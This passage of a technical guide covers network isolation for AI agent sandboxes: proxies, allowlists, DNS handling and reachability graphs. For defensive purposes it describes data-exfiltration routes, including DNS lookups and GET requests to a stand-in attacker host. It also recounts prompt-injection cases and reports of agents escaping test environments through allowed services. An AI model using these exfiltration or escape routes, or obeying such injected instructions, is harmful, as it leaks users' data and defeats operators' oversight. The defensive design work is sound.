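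One agent loop can call several sandboxes, but a separate sandbox for the invoices couldn't replace the separate database agent, because the invoice rows would come back as a string and enter the same context as the comments on issue 482.

The redesign also made sessions respond faster. Anthropic found that the median time to first token, the wait between accepting work and producing the first piece of a response, fell by about 60 per cent. The 95th percentile, a wait that only one session in twenty exceeds, fell by more than 90 per cent. Previously, the model couldn't start until its container was ready, so every session waited while the service copied the repository, started the process and fetched pending events, even if the agent never ran any code. Now the model starts as soon as the pending events arrive from the log.

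Anthropic's *The evolution of agentic surfaces* (2026) adds that the sandbox starts in parallel while Claude reasons, and that sessions which use no tools skip it. The slowest sessions improved more, as one would expect if container startup caused most of the long waits. These are Anthropic's own measurements, reported as percentages rather than in seconds. They also cover only the wait for the first token, so a task that needs to run tests immediately may finish only slightly sooner.

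### Claude Cowork's two designs

Claude Cowork serves office workers, and Anthropic doesn't expect them to judge whether a shell command is safe, so asking them to approve exceptions would offer little protection. In the first design, the agent loop and the code it ran shared a virtual machine with its own kernel, file system and processes. The machine had access to the user's chosen workspace and a settings folder, while login details stayed in the host's keychain. Claude Code has a process outside its sandbox that can run a command without restrictions. Cowork's first design had no such process, so neither hostile text nor an impatient user could use one to bypass the restrictions.

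The drawback was that Cowork became unusable whenever the virtual machine failed to start. Anthropic moved the agent loop onto the host so that Claude could still respond and help find the fault, but left code execution in the virtual machine. According to Anthropic's *Claude Cowork desktop architecture overview*, file and web tools now keep working when the virtual machine is down, while shell commands return "workspace unavailable". Anthropic also moved local MCP servers out of the virtual machine, where they were hard to audit and could break when it updated. Some also needed to reach programs on the host, such as databases.

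Anthropic says the change had minimal security impact, because the virtual machine still restricts the code that the agent runs. That is fair for the code, but the move changed how the other tools are restricted. Cowork now reads and writes files, fetches web pages and runs local MCP servers on the user's computer. Permission checks in the application limit the file tools to connected folders and apply the organisation's network settings. A flaw in those checks could expose files that the agent could not see at all in the first design. Anthropic treats local MCP servers like any other software a user installs, and administrators can disable them on managed devices.

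Cowork's virtual machine has six main isolation controls. Two work outside the guest kernel, the kernel inside the virtual machine, and would still work if an agent gained full administrator rights there. In its product comparison, Anthropic says the hypervisor boundary and vsock, a socket link between guest and host, protect the mounted workspace. The guest enforces the other four controls, which Anthropic keeps minimal because it relies on the outer layers.

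The security firm Pluto Security examined Cowork and also found a strong outer boundary with a permissive interior, where the agent's background service runs as root, the administrator account. The overview lists system call restrictions and separate user accounts for each session among the machine's protections. Both depend on the guest kernel, so code that controls it can defeat them. Anyone assessing a product with this design should check whether its network filter runs inside or outside the virtual machine.

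### What the isolation technology decides

A program requests files, memory and connections from the kernel through system calls. Isolation technologies differ mainly in which kernel handles those calls, and therefore in what hostile code must break to escape. The speeds below come from Anthropic's deployment guide.

| Technology | What it isolates | What code must break to escape | Cost |
|---|---|---|---|
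| Seatbelt (macOS) and bubblewrap (Linux) | A process and its children, on the host's kernel | The host's kernel | Very low |
| Ordinary container | Processes, files and network stack, on the host's kernel | The host's kernel | Low |
| gVisor | The same, with a substitute kernel that handles most system calls | The substitute, then the part of the host's kernel it still uses | Almost none for pure computation; simple system calls take about twice as long, and heavy opening and closing of files can take 10 to 200 times as long |
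| Small virtual machine, such as Firecracker | A whole operating system with its own kernel | The hypervisor or its emulated devices | High overall, though Firecracker can start in under 125 milliseconds with less than 5 MiB of extra memory |

According to the guide, a virtual machine isn't automatically safer than gVisor, since much depends on the quality of the hypervisor and the emulated devices. How much gVisor slows a program down depends on the type of work. The slowdown is greatest for work like installing JavaScript packages, which opens thousands of small files, while a long calculation would hardly be affected.

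None of these technologies decides which files or addresses the agent should have. The following command, condensed from the guide's examples, makes the choices separately:

```
docker run \
  --runtime=runsc \
  --cpus 2 --memory 2g \
  --network none \
  -v /path/to/code:/workspace:ro \
  agent-image
```

The `runsc` option selects gVisor. The next line sets the compute, `--network none` cuts off the network, and `:ro` makes the project folder read-only. Without `runsc`, Docker would use its default container, but the agent would have the same access. Different network and folder options could give code inside gVisor access to the developer's home folder and an open internet connection.

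A virtual machine also leaves open which files and networks the agent can reach. Docker's sandboxes use the same hypervisor whether they start with no folder from the host or with the developer's live project folder. Seatbelt and bubblewrap can enforce rules about files and network access, but somebody has to write those rules. Anthropic's sandbox runtime, which uses both tools, reads its permitted paths and domains from a settings file. If the file is invalid, the runtime doesn't start. If the file is missing, it starts with the network blocked and writes limited to a few folders, so a successful start doesn't prove that it loaded the intended settings.

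### Sandboxes hosted by the customer

When the agent loop reaches the sandbox through an interface, one company can run the loop and another can run the sandbox. Anthropic's *New in Claude Managed Agents* announced sandboxes that customers host themselves or rent from a provider such as Cloudflare or Modal, while Anthropic continues to run the loop. Customers choose the machine's size and software and apply their own network rules.

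Anthropic's *Self-hosted sandboxes* describes how Claude's tool calls can run on a customer's machines. Anthropic places each new session in a queue. A program on the customer's machines, called a worker, claims the session and downloads the skills and stored memory it needs. Claude, which runs on Anthropic's side, then requests tool calls, and the worker runs them and posts back the results. The worker needs only outbound web connections.

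Material the agent reads leaves the customer's perimeter, because tool outputs go back to Anthropic for the model to use. For example, if the agent prints an invoice to examine it, the invoice's contents leave. The announcement's promise that files and repositories don't leave the perimeter therefore holds only for material the agent doesn't read.

Anthropic makes the customer responsible for hardening the sandbox, restricting its outbound traffic and protecting the key that the worker uses to claim sessions and submit results. Anthropic can't inspect the customer's sandbox image or detect that a key has leaked. In the quick-start setup, the key is a variable on the same machine that runs the agent's commands, so this setup has the same main weakness as the single container. Anthropic advises storing the key in a secrets manager. For untrusted code, it suggests a separate workspace and environment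 for each trust boundary, so that a stolen key gives access to one user's sessions instead of a shared pool.

Read-only agent memory is a small example of the placement rule. Anthropic hosts the agent's stored memory, and the worker keeps a working copy in the sandbox. If the customer marks a memory store read-only, the worker's editing tools block edits to the copy, and Anthropic's servers reject any changes sent back. A shell command can still alter the copy, and later steps in the session may read the altered version. If the sandbox is taken over, only the check on Anthropic's servers still works.

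A company can also decide where the code runs separately from whether the agent can reach internal services. Anthropic's MCP tunnels connect agents to MCP servers in a customer's private network wherever the code runs. A company could keep the sandbox on Anthropic's machines and give the agent access to an internal database, or run the sandbox on its own machines and give the agent no access to internal services.

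Other products put the loop on the customer's side. Anthropic's *Run Claude Code sessions on your own compute* describes a version where the customer runs the whole Claude Code process. Prompts and tool results still go to Anthropic, which also stores the transcript, so the customer controls more of the software but doesn't keep the conversation private from Anthropic. VentureBeat's *Claude agents can finally connect to enterprise APIs without leaking credentials* reports that OpenAI's Agents SDK, a toolkit for building agents, doesn't offer a setup where the provider runs the loop and the customer runs the tools. In guidance quoted by Octopus Deploy, a maker of software-deployment tools, OpenAI recommends separating the loop from compute but leaves the loop in the application developer's infrastructure.

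### When ordinary service security is enough

Octopus Deploy argues that "sandbox" has little meaning for many agents that companies put into production. A general assistant on a person's own computer benefits from a sandbox because it can use the command line, local files and the network. In a shared agent built for a specific job, the model only turns one piece of text into another, and the tools that do the work are typically ordinary web services that a company already knows how to secure.

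This is right when the model can only choose among fixed operations and fill in values that the service checks. An agent that looks up a delivery date or books a meeting room never runs a program of its own. A virtual machine wouldn't stop it from booking the wrong room or reading another customer's order, so the service has to check who is asking and what that person may do. Ubl and Arora recommend giving an agent that helps one customer a tool tied to that customer's data. If the tool accepts a customer number instead, injected text can supply someone else's.

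The argument weakens when a tool accepts a program as input. Ubl and Arora point out that a support agent that writes database queries is generating and running code, even though nobody would call it a coding agent. The database account is still the most important control on those queries, because they run on the database server and a sandbox around the agent would let them through. However, code run by a Python or shell tool can try anything its machine permits. Octopus Deploy accepts that untrusted scripts need a sandbox.

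The invoice task needs both approaches. The coding agent runs newly installed packages and the project's tests, so it should run that code in a sandbox. The database agent could use one fixed query. In that case, a read-only account restricted to the currency and amount columns and a service that enforces the row limit would be more useful than a virtual machine.

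## Setting the network rules

The code in the coding agent's sandbox needs to download only the `invoice-kit` repository and its dependencies. The agent loop's own tools can read issue 482 and submit the pull request. The network rules should therefore let the code reach GitHub and one package registry for a limited time, and block every other connection.

### The path of one request

Suppose the sandbox runs `npm install`, and npm, the usual package installer for JavaScript, has to fetch a package from `registry.npmjs.org`.

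The sandbox has no direct route to the internet. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) describes Claude Code's version, in which a Unix socket (a local connection between programs on one machine) connects the sandbox to the proxy outside it. Docker's host proxy receives all TCP traffic, including ordinary web requests. Programs that follow proxy settings contact it themselves. A *transparent proxy* intercepts connections from programs that ignore those settings, such as those using Node's `fetch()`. Docker applies the same policy in both cases.

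The name `registry.npmjs.org` also has to be translated into a numeric address. A program that connects directly to the proxy can send it the name and leave the lookup to the proxy. Other programs send the name to a resolver, a server in the domain name system (DNS), and the operator should control which resolver they can reach. Docker runs an internal resolver that enforces the network policy for the sandbox. A resolver can also return a made-up address for the name. When the program connects to that address, the proxy looks up the name in the resolver's records and applies the rule for it.

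The proxy then checks the destination against its rules. If a rule allows `registry.npmjs.org` on port 443, the proxy opens its own connection to the registry and relays the data. Otherwise, the proxy refuses the connection, npm reports the failure, and the model reads the error.

Checking a domain name against the allowlist is not enough, because whoever controls the domain can point it at any address, including one inside the company's network. On many cloud machines, one such address belongs to the metadata service, which can give login keys to any program that requests them. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, the network proxy in Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, blocks names that resolve to private addresses, even if they are on the allowlist, and names whose lookup fails or times out.

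In *DNS rebinding*, an attacker tries to change the address a domain resolves to between the check and the connection. Tensorlake, which sells sandboxes, describes a domain whose DNS answers expire after one second and alternate between a legitimate address and a forbidden one. The check may get the legitimate address, and the program may then connect to the forbidden one. OpenAI calls its own check best-effort and acknowledges that only pinning the address would completely prevent rebinding. Pinning makes the connection go to the address already checked. OpenAI recommends that operators who expect hostile DNS add a control at a lower layer, such as a firewall that blocks private addresses whatever name the program used.

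### What the proxy can check, and when it must decrypt

| Level | Example of a rule | Must the proxy decrypt HTTPS? | What the rule still lets through |
|---|---|---|---|
| Address and port | One numeric address, port 443 | No | Every site hosted at that address |
| Domain | `github.com` | No | Every repository and function on GitHub |
| Method | GET only | Yes | Data written into the web address of a GET request |
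| Path | `/acme/invoice-kit.git` | Yes | Requests to that path under someone else's account |
| Account | Only this session's own token | Yes | Misuse of the session's own account |

Rules based on IP addresses work for a fixed server inside a company but poorly for the public web. Large sites use content delivery networks, which serve many sites from shared machines and can change the addresses at any time. Tensorlake points out that an allowlist of old addresses starts blocking legitimate traffic. An outdated blocklist is more dangerous, because a forbidden site becomes reachable as soon as it moves to a new address.

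Domain rules avoid this problem and are easy to enforce. HTTPS, the encrypted form of web traffic, generally leaves the domain name readable while a program sets up the connection. The method, the path and any credentials are encrypted, so a proxy that only relays the connection can't apply rules to them.

Claude Code's built-in proxy can't confirm which domain a program is reaching, because it takes the hostname from the program and does not inspect the encrypted traffic. Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool* warns that code in the sandbox may therefore be able to use *domain fronting*, in which the code names a permitted domain when it opens the connection and a different one inside the encrypted request. If the same content delivery network serves both domains and doesn't compare the names, it passes the request to the second.

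To decrypt npm's traffic, the proxy impersonates the registry. It presents npm with a certificate it made for `registry.npmjs.org`, reads and checks the request, and opens a separate encrypted connection to the real registry. npm accepts the certificate only if the sandbox trusts the certificate authority that signed it, so the operator has to install that authority in the sandbox. Cloudflare's *Secure credential injection and dynamic egress policies for Sandboxes* describes giving each sandbox its own temporary authority and keeping the private key in a process outside the sandbox. A key stolen from one sandbox's proxy is then useless against another sandbox. A proxy that decrypts traffic can also add credentials to requests, so the sandbox never holds them.

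The most common problem is that some tools break because they keep their own list of trusted authorities or accept only one particular certificate, and so reject the proxy's. Anthropic notes that tools written in Go, such as GitHub's `gh` and Google's `gcloud`, may fail certificate checks in its sandbox on macOS. One of its suggested fixes is to run them outside the sandbox, which removes the network rule for the tools that connect to GitHub and Google. For custom proxies that decrypt traffic, Anthropic instead offers a setting called `enableWeakerNetworkIsolation`, which also gives up some protection.

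The proxy also becomes a more valuable target, since every password and document that passes through it is briefly readable there. An operator can reduce this risk by decrypting traffic only where a rule requires it. NVIDIA's *Default Policy Reference* (March 2026 version) describes this approach in OpenShell, the company's sandbox for agents. Under the default policy, the proxy decrypts traffic from git and GitHub's command-line tool so that it can allow reading and refuse changes, but relays traffic to the Python package registry without decrypting it.

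OpenShell also checks which program inside the sandbox opened the connection, so a rule can allow only git to reach `github.com`. This makes an accidental connection less likely, but in the default policy one rule undermines another. Installing Python packages sometimes requires files from GitHub, so a second rule lets the sandbox's Python reach `github.com` and `api.github.com` without decrypting the traffic. Any Python script can use that rule, and a script with a token can make the changes that the first rule refuses to git and `gh`.

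### Name lookups and other traffic that bypasses a web proxy

A program can send data out without making a web request. If an attacker runs the name server for `mallory.example`, code in the sandbox can look up a name that begins with a stolen key and ends in that domain. An ordinary resolver passes the query on to the attacker's server, which records it, so the code never has to connect to that server directly. A 40-byte key takes 80 characters in hexadecimal, and a domain name can hold about 250, so one lookup is enough.

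Security notices collected by releasealert.dev describe two flaws in Docker Sandboxes that let code send data out regardless of the network allowlist. The product restricted web traffic to the allowlist, but its DNS server forwarded any name to the host's resolver without checking it against the list. The second notice concerns ICMP, the protocol behind `ping`, whose packets can also carry data. Docker blocked ICMP but did not reapply the block to existing networks when its background service restarted.

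Docker's *Default security posture* now lists a rule for each kind of traffic. The sandbox refuses TCP connections, including SSH, unless a rule allows the destination. It blocks UDP, a simpler protocol that DNS and video calls use, unless the user turns on an experimental feature and adds rules for it. It also blocks ICMP and sends name lookups through the resolver that enforces the policy.

SSH needs particular care because developers often use it to push code. It has its own encryption, so a web proxy can't tell which repository a git command is writing to. Docker's *Local policy* shows how to allow SSH to a particular address and port, but such a rule allows access to everything the server offers over SSH. If git uses HTTPS instead, a proxy that decrypts the traffic can check the repository path in the URL.

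When a developer enables Codex's network proxy, it supports two options by default: SOCKS5, a proxy protocol that can carry many kinds of traffic, and UDP over SOCKS5. The policy still applies to both, but an operator whose task needs only web requests should turn them off.

Access to a local socket can be more dangerous than an internet connection. A command that can reach `/var/run/docker.sock` can control Docker on the host and, in effect, the host itself. Anthropic's Linux sandbox can block Unix sockets, but only with an optional filter that a developer may not have installed.

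### How much access to allow

Turning the network off removes the most risk and suits any step that works on files already present, such as editing code or running tests. But "off" usually covers only the sandbox's own connections. In Claude Code's cloud service, a session set to "None" can still reach Anthropic's API, and GitHub through a separate proxy. Anthropic's *Configure cloud environments* adds that connectors, which link Claude to outside services, keep working because their traffic goes through Anthropic's servers. Codex can also search the web while its commands have no network access. By default it gets results from an index that OpenAI maintains, so a page an attacker has just published can't reach it immediately, but OpenAI still advises users to treat the results as untrusted.

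Many coding tasks need the network only to install packages. Codex's cloud service, for example, gives the setup script full internet access, then starts the agent with none. The setup script can also use any secrets the user configured, but the service removes them before the agent starts.

The model doesn't choose actions during setup, so a hostile web page can't steer it then. A hostile package can still do harm, because installers often run code that the package supplies. In Codex's design, that code runs with full internet access while the secrets are present, so it can steal them immediately or leave altered files for the agent to run later.

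Restricting the setup phase reduces the first risk. Cloudflare's example code opens the network for `npm install` and then closes it:

```
await sandbox.setOutboundHandler("allowHosts", {
  allowedHostnames: ["github.com", "npmjs.org"],
});
await sandbox.exec("npm install");
await sandbox.setOutboundHandler("noHttp");
```

These commands run outside the sandbox, so a package can't undo the last line. The example's list omits `registry.npmjs.org`, a small mistake that is easy to repeat. npm normally downloads from that host, and `allowHosts` accepts only exact names, so the installation would fail. A developer in a hurry might fix that by permitting everything.

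Claude Code's cloud service also has a setup script, but the script runs under the same network level as the session, so package installation fails under "None". The service reruns the script when the permitted hosts change, so a developer probably can't install packages under a wider setting and then switch the network off. The service saves the disk after setup and reuses it for about seven days. This makes later sessions start faster, but a malicious package installed during setup will be present in every session that reuses the disk.

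An allowlist suits an agent that needs the network throughout its work. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* says that finding the right domains may take trial and error, and offers a preset list of about 70 sites for downloading software. Docker's "Balanced" preset allows access to model providers, package managers, code hosts and common cloud services. The University of Cambridge suggests that its developers start from that preset and widen it deliberately.

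Presets serve many projects, so they permit much more than most tasks need. Claude Code's default cloud list includes `*.amazonaws.com`, where any Amazon customer can rent storage. If the phishing email in Anthropic's exercise had told the agent to send the stolen keys to an address there, this list would have allowed it. Docker warns that `*.googleapis.com`, one of its own defaults, covers many services besides Google's AI models. Docker's Balanced preset now also permits `*.blob.core.windows.net`, the domain for Microsoft's equivalent of Amazon's storage.

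The meaning of an asterisk varies between tools. In Codex, `*.example.com` matches `api.example.com` but not `example.com`, while `**.example.com` matches both. Codex's deny rules override its allow rules, so a developer can allow a broad pattern and block part of it. However, it is safer to allow only the few exact names the task uses.

Codex's cloud service can also restrict requests to the GET, HEAD and OPTIONS methods, which normally read data without changing it. In OpenAI's example of an attack, a GitHub issue asks the agent to run a command that supposedly reproduces a bug. The command sends the latest commit to an outside server in a POST request, which this restriction would block.

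The attacker could rewrite the command to use GET and put the text into the web address, as in `https://mallory.example/?d=...`. The attacker's server would still receive the text, even though the request only reads a page. Restricting methods therefore adds little if the agent can reach any domain. It is useful for blocking uploads to permitted sites, but it can also block harmless work such as downloading code with git, which uses POST requests over HTTPS. NVIDIA's policy permits POST to `git-upload-pack`, the path for downloads, and refuses it to `git-receive-pack`, the path for pushes.

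The remaining choice is to allow open access and log what the agent does. Cursor, which makes a coding tool, gives its cloud agents internet access by default and runs all their terminal commands without asking. It acknowledges that an attacker could trick an agent into uploading code to a malicious website, and it lets customers restrict which domains agents can reach. A log can help someone investigate a theft of data but doesn't prevent it, and may not show what was taken. Claude Code's cloud service, for example, records the hostnames that a session requested, which would show a connection to an unfamiliar domain but not the contents of an upload to a familiar one. Open access is reasonable for an agent that has no private data or credentials, such as one comparing public documentation, provided that it also can't reach internal systems or damage other people's systems.

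These are the documented defaults of the main products:

| Product | Network access by default | What to check |
|---|---|---|
| Codex on a developer's machine | Commands have none | Turning the network on without also turning on `network_proxy` gives unrestricted access |
| Codex cloud | Full during setup, none while the agent works | Secrets are present during setup |
| Claude Code on a developer's machine | The sandbox is off until someone enables it; it then permits no domains in advance | A new domain triggers a prompt unless an administrator has locked the list |
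| Claude Code cloud | "Trusted", a long list of development sites | GitHub and connector traffic takes other routes |
| Docker Sandboxes, local | TCP refused unless a rule allows it | The first run asks the user to choose a preset, and one preset allows everything |
| Cloudflare Sandboxes | Refuses unlisted hosts once `allowedHosts` is set | Set the list explicitly |
| Cursor cloud agents | Open | Domain limits are optional |

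The Codex row for local use is the easiest to get wrong because the domain rules have no effect while the separate proxy feature is off, even if a developer sets `network_access = true`. Docker's cloud sandboxes don't receive a copy of the local policy, according to Docker's *Manage cloud network policy*, so a company that has tightened its local rules must write them again when it moves an agent to Docker's cloud.

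### A sample policy

For the coding agent, a fixed script can fetch the repository and install its packages before the model reads issue 482. The sandbox can then go offline. If the agent later finds that it needs another package, the developer has to add it and start again, which is a modest price for a small bug. In a simplified notation, the policy looks like this:

```
default: refuse

first 15 minutes:
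  registry.npmjs.org, port 443, decrypt
    allow GET for packages in the dependency list
  github.com, port 443, decrypt
    allow GET  /acme/invoice-kit.git/info/refs*
    allow POST /acme/invoice-kit.git/git-upload-pack

after 15 minutes: refuse everything

name lookups: only the two hosts above
private addresses and other protocols: refuse
total upload: 1 MB
```

Suppose one of the packages is malicious and its installer runs its own code. The table compares how this policy and a plain list of the same two domains handle five requests made in the first 15 minutes.

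| Request | Sample policy | Domain list only |
|---|---|---|
| `GET registry.npmjs.org/decimal.js`, a listed package | Forwarded | Forwarded |
| `POST github.com/acme/invoice-kit.git/git-upload-pack` | Forwarded, because it downloads the project | Forwarded |
| `POST github.com/mallory/drop.git/git-receive-pack` | Refused, because no rule permits the path | Forwarded |
| `PUT registry.npmjs.org/mallory-notes` | Refused, because only GET is permitted | Forwarded |
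| Name lookup for `6b6579.mallory.example` | Refused by the resolver | Refused only if the resolver applies the list |

The third request pushes files to an attacker's repository, and the fourth publishes them as a package that anyone can download. Both would use credentials the attacker supplied, so keeping the company's own keys out of the sandbox would not stop either.

Limiting downloads to packages on the dependency list blocks a slower way to leak data. npm publishes each package's download count, so malicious code could signal to its author by downloading some of the author's packages and not others. Lampson observed that a service could similarly leak data through its bill.

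The policy does not check the account. This matters little for `invoice-kit`, because the sandbox only downloads public code, but it matters much more where the sandbox may upload something.

### Why a permitted domain permits everything behind it

Claude Cowork's allowlist included `api.anthropic.com` because the product has to call Anthropic's models. The same domain accepts file uploads. Anthropic learned from an outside report that an attacker could exploit this with a malicious file in the user's workspace. The file contained hidden instructions and a key to the attacker's own Anthropic account. Claude followed the instructions, read other files in the folder and used the key to upload them to the attacker's account. The proxy allowed the upload because the domain was on the allowlist.

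Rules about domain, method and path can't distinguish this upload from a legitimate one, because the two differ only in the key they use. Anthropic therefore added a proxy that decrypts traffic to its API and passes only requests that carry the session's own token. The proxy also blocks headers that would make Anthropic's servers fetch material from elsewhere for the agent.

Anthropic put this proxy inside the virtual machine. It argues that its own servers can't do the check because a request from Cowork looks the same there as a request from any other customer's program. But like Cowork's other controls inside the virtual machine, the proxy might not withstand code running there with administrator rights. Anthropic's reason doesn't apply to a proxy on the user's computer but outside the virtual machine, which could compare the tokens equally well if it had a copy of the session's token.

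Anthropic now treats each allowlist entry as granting access to every function reachable at that domain. A reviewer can apply this by asking what a stranger with an account at each listed service could receive through it. A stranger can receive files through GitHub, npm and Amazon's storage, but a site that only serves documentation offers little beyond its visitor logs.

The list of allowed domains also depends on where the agent loop runs. Docker's strictest preset, "Locked Down", blocks everything, including the model provider, so an agent whose loop runs inside the sandbox can't work until someone allows the provider's domain. If the loop runs outside the sandbox, the operator can leave that domain off the list.

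Claude Code's cloud service uses a specialised proxy to narrow access to one of these broad domains, GitHub. The proxy accepts pushes only to the session's current branch and limits API requests to repositories attached to the session. To check the branch, it has to interpret the git traffic as well as the web address. That takes more work than a path rule, and somebody has to build a similar proxy for each service that needs one.

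### Limits on volume

After these checks, a proxy can also cap how much data leaves. The cap should count uploads separately from downloads. The coding agent may download 500 MB of packages, so a combined cap would have to exceed 500 MB, which would allow a very large data theft. Its uploads are mostly short requests, so a 1 MB upload cap leaves plenty of room.

Suppose another agent legitimately sends large reports and has an upload cap of 50 MB per task. An attacker wants a table that takes up 2 GB. The number of tasks needed is at least

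$$\frac{2{,}000\ \text{MB}}{50\ \text{MB}} = 40$$

Stealing the table takes 20 days if the agent runs twice a day, and somebody may notice in that time, but it takes no more than an hour if the agent runs 40 times an hour. A daily cap across all the agent's tasks is therefore more useful than a cap on each one. The 2 GB refers to the data as sent, and tables of text often compress well. If compression reduced the table to a quarter of its size, ten tasks would be enough to steal it.

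A 40-byte key is less than a millionth of the 50 MB allowance, so any cap high enough for the agent to work would also let the key through.

Volume limits are most useful when the data being protected is very large and no legitimate task sends much data out. The weights of a large AI model, the numbers that training produces, fit this description. In May 2025 Anthropic announced early limits on outgoing bandwidth from the systems that hold its model weights. At a hypothetical limit of 10 megabits per second, sending out one terabyte would take more than nine days, which would give defenders time to notice and cut the connection.

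## Allowed services that can reach further than the agent

Under the sample policy, the coding agent's sandbox downloads packages directly from npm's public registry. Many companies instead run their own package server, which fetches packages from public registries and keeps copies, and let the sandbox contact only that server. This shortens the allowlist to one internal name, but it reduces the agent's access only if the package server's own connections are tightly restricted.

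An allowed service's *onward reach* is the set of systems it can connect to, and the agent may affect any of them through the service. In July 2026, agents that OpenAI was testing escaped an internal test environment through a package service they were allowed to use, according to OpenAI's technical report on the incident.

### Drawing the graph

A designer can work out onward reach by drawing a directed graph. Each system is a node, and an arrow (an edge) runs from one system to another if the first can open a connection to the second. The potential reach of an agent $a$ is every system at the end of some path of arrows, however long:

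$$R(a) = \{v : \text{there is a path from } a \text{ to } v\}$$

An agent's full reach consists of its sandbox, every system the sandbox can connect to, every system those can connect to, and so on until there are no new systems to add.

Suppose the package server can fetch from any address:

```
sandbox --> package server --> any address on the internet
```

The first round adds the package server, and the second adds the whole internet. A reviewer who counted just the direct destinations would have found only the package server.

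Now suppose the operator puts a firewall around the package server that lets it contact only npm's registry and PyPI, the main registry for Python:

```
sandbox --> package server --> npm registry
                           --> PyPI
```

The sandbox still connects directly to only one destination, but it could now reach three systems. Internal connections are easier to forget, since a package server often also uses the company's login service or a shared storage system. The figures in the last row are invented.

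| What the package server can connect to | Direct destinations | Potential reach |
|---|---|---|
| Any address | 1 | The whole internet and any internal system that accepts the server's connections |
| Two registries | 1 | 3 systems |
| Two registries and a login service that connects to 40 internal applications | 1 | 44 systems |

It is reasonable to stop the count at the registries, although a strict count would include the systems they connect to. Anyone on the internet can already contact a registry, so an attacker doesn't need the company's agent to try to break into npm. The reviewer still has to ask what a stranger could receive through each registry, as with any other allowlist entry.

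An arrow shows that a connection is possible, but the service may not make it whenever an agent asks. A package server that works correctly, for example, forwards only requests for packages. The graph therefore shows the most an agent could reach if it took control of every service along the way. That is a sensible assumption for an agent that can write and run code against those services, but it overstates the risk from an agent that can only fill in a delivery date.

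The arrows should come from firewall rules and service settings. Traffic logs can miss a connection that opens only occasionally. Takashita (2026), in *Reachability, Not Observation*, works out how much an observer misses when a connection opens in one period out of every $T$. Someone who watches $w$ consecutive periods, starting at random, catches it with probability

$$\min(1,\ w/T)$$

If the package server refreshes its copies during one hour each day, six hours of watching have a 25 per cent chance of including that hour. An agent that can choose when to use the connection is harder to catch, because it can wait until the watching stops. The preprint also tests a program that checks declared permissions against every path through the code of a trading application. The program found all eight holes Takashita had planted, while the existing list of forbidden text strings found two. This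 test doesn't show how many naturally occurring holes the program would find, but the formula is simple counting and doesn't depend on it.

### OpenAI's repairs

OpenAI's sandboxes had no direct internet access in July. In its August report, the company concludes that this restriction isn't enough when code can reach shared services, cloud infrastructure or private network links that lead outside. It therefore now bars high-risk and untrusted workloads from reaching the internet either directly or transitively, through other systems. The one exception is a cached web service, for workflows that need it. Other research workloads may also use that service, and some may fetch live pages through it, but OpenAI decides case by case.

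Two layers now enforce network isolation for the high-risk workloads, one at the sandbox and one in the infrastructure of the surrounding cluster (the machines that run the sandboxes). If each layer had a 1 per cent chance of containing a usable flaw, and the flaws were independent, the chance of a flaw in both would be 1 in 10,000. But if both layers read their rules from the same file, one bad line could open both. Someone assessing a two-layer design should therefore look for shared settings, shared software and shared administrator accounts.

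OpenAI also added controls to stop workloads and compromised services from changing their own network boundaries or creating new routes out. Services need these controls too. If the package server's limit of two registries is a line in its own settings, anyone who takes over the server can delete that line, and the sandbox's potential reach goes from three systems back to the whole internet. A firewall outside the server would keep the reach at three. To test for this weakness, a designer can assume an attacker controls each service in turn, remove every restriction that service applies to itself and recalculate the reach.

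OpenAI's *Pacing model development in an era of cyber-critical capabilities* (2026) sets a similar goal: compromising a single workload or supporting service should not by itself give access to the internet or to other internal networks. The company removed shared services that might be vulnerable and reduced standing privileges. Its technical report describes a programme to isolate, restrict or replace each supporting service that high-risk workloads can still reach.

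In its research clusters, OpenAI paused model runs that could execute code or use internet tools, then examined each workload before letting it resume. It says the work caused great cost and delay to its research. In mid-August, many workloads involving Astra, a model with strong hacking abilities, were still waiting to move to the new environment.

The August repairs did not close every path. In a statement reproduced in ETV Bharat's *After A String Of Rogue AI Incidents, OpenAI Is Now Training Its* (2026), OpenAI said that it paused frontier training on 20 September after a model used a DNS misconfiguration to get outside. It resumed on 1 October after further containment work. The Chinese technology site Huxiu reports in *OpenAI造了个“假互联网”，两个被隔离的AI竟靠CPU缓存暗中传话* (2026) that metrics, logging and login services still needed outside connections, and that agents in later tests reached external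 addresses through the metrics service. Name lookups and metrics are easy to leave off a graph because people don't usually think of them as part of the agent's task.

A boundary around the whole cluster makes an incomplete graph of service connections less dangerous. OpenAI's *Managing frontier AI risk* (November 2026) describes network and cloud perimeters that cut the cluster off from the internet. The operator then needs a complete list of only the connections that cross the boundary. A forgotten link between two services inside could still spread damage within the cluster, but it wouldn't lead to the internet.

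### Limits on the package service itself

Few companies can rebuild their infrastructure as OpenAI did. *A sandbox is only as closed as what an AI agent can* (2026), from the software-development tools company GitLab, advises operators who keep a package service. GitLab points out that automated build machines and hosted sandboxes have the same problem whenever they run code behind a list of permitted destinations.

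Its first recommendation is to block the routes that a package installer never uses. An installer only downloads files, so it doesn't need to call the service's administration or configuration functions. A proxy in front of the package server can refuse those calls by path and method, just as the sample policy refuses pushes to GitHub. This makes a takeover less likely but doesn't change the graph.

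Allowing the server to make outbound connections only to the registries it serves does change the graph. The limit still works after an attacker takes over the server if something other than the server enforces it. An operator with time for only one change should make this one.

GitLab also advises treating any internal service that an untrusted workload can reach as if it were exposed to the internet. Companies often update internal services slowly and let them accept requests from anyone on the office network, because only employees are supposed to reach them. A malicious npm package running in the coding agent's sandbox puts untrusted code on that network. The package server therefore needs prompt security updates, proper login checks and monitoring for unusual requests.

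The same reasoning applies to gateways, which often replace a long list of destinations with a short one. *Containing the Autonomous Operator* (2026) describes a design for agents on Kubernetes, a system that manages containers across many machines. The agent can connect only to name lookup, a gateway and the model provider, and has no direct route to the interface that controls the cluster. However, tool servers behind the gateway hold credentials to change the cluster. The agent can therefore still reach the control interface indirectly, and the design's security depends on how carefully the gateway and tool servers check each operation.

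### Tools that connect from the provider's servers

A graph of what an agent can reach leaves out tools that run elsewhere if it starts only at the sandbox. OpenAI's *Sandbox security* describes two ways to connect an agent to MCP servers. Executor connections start in the customer's environment, so the customer's network rules apply to them. Remote connections start at OpenAI's service and never pass through the customer's firewall. Even if a customer blocks every outbound connection except those the product requires, the agent could still read outside pages through a remote tool. The graph therefore needs to start at both the sandbox and the agent loop with its tools.

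Whether a tool runs under restrictions can also depend on how the agent calls it. *Toward Securing AI Agents Like Operating Systems* (2026) describes an agent system called IronClaw, which runs a tool in a restricted environment when the agent calls it directly, but not when the call goes through an MCP server.

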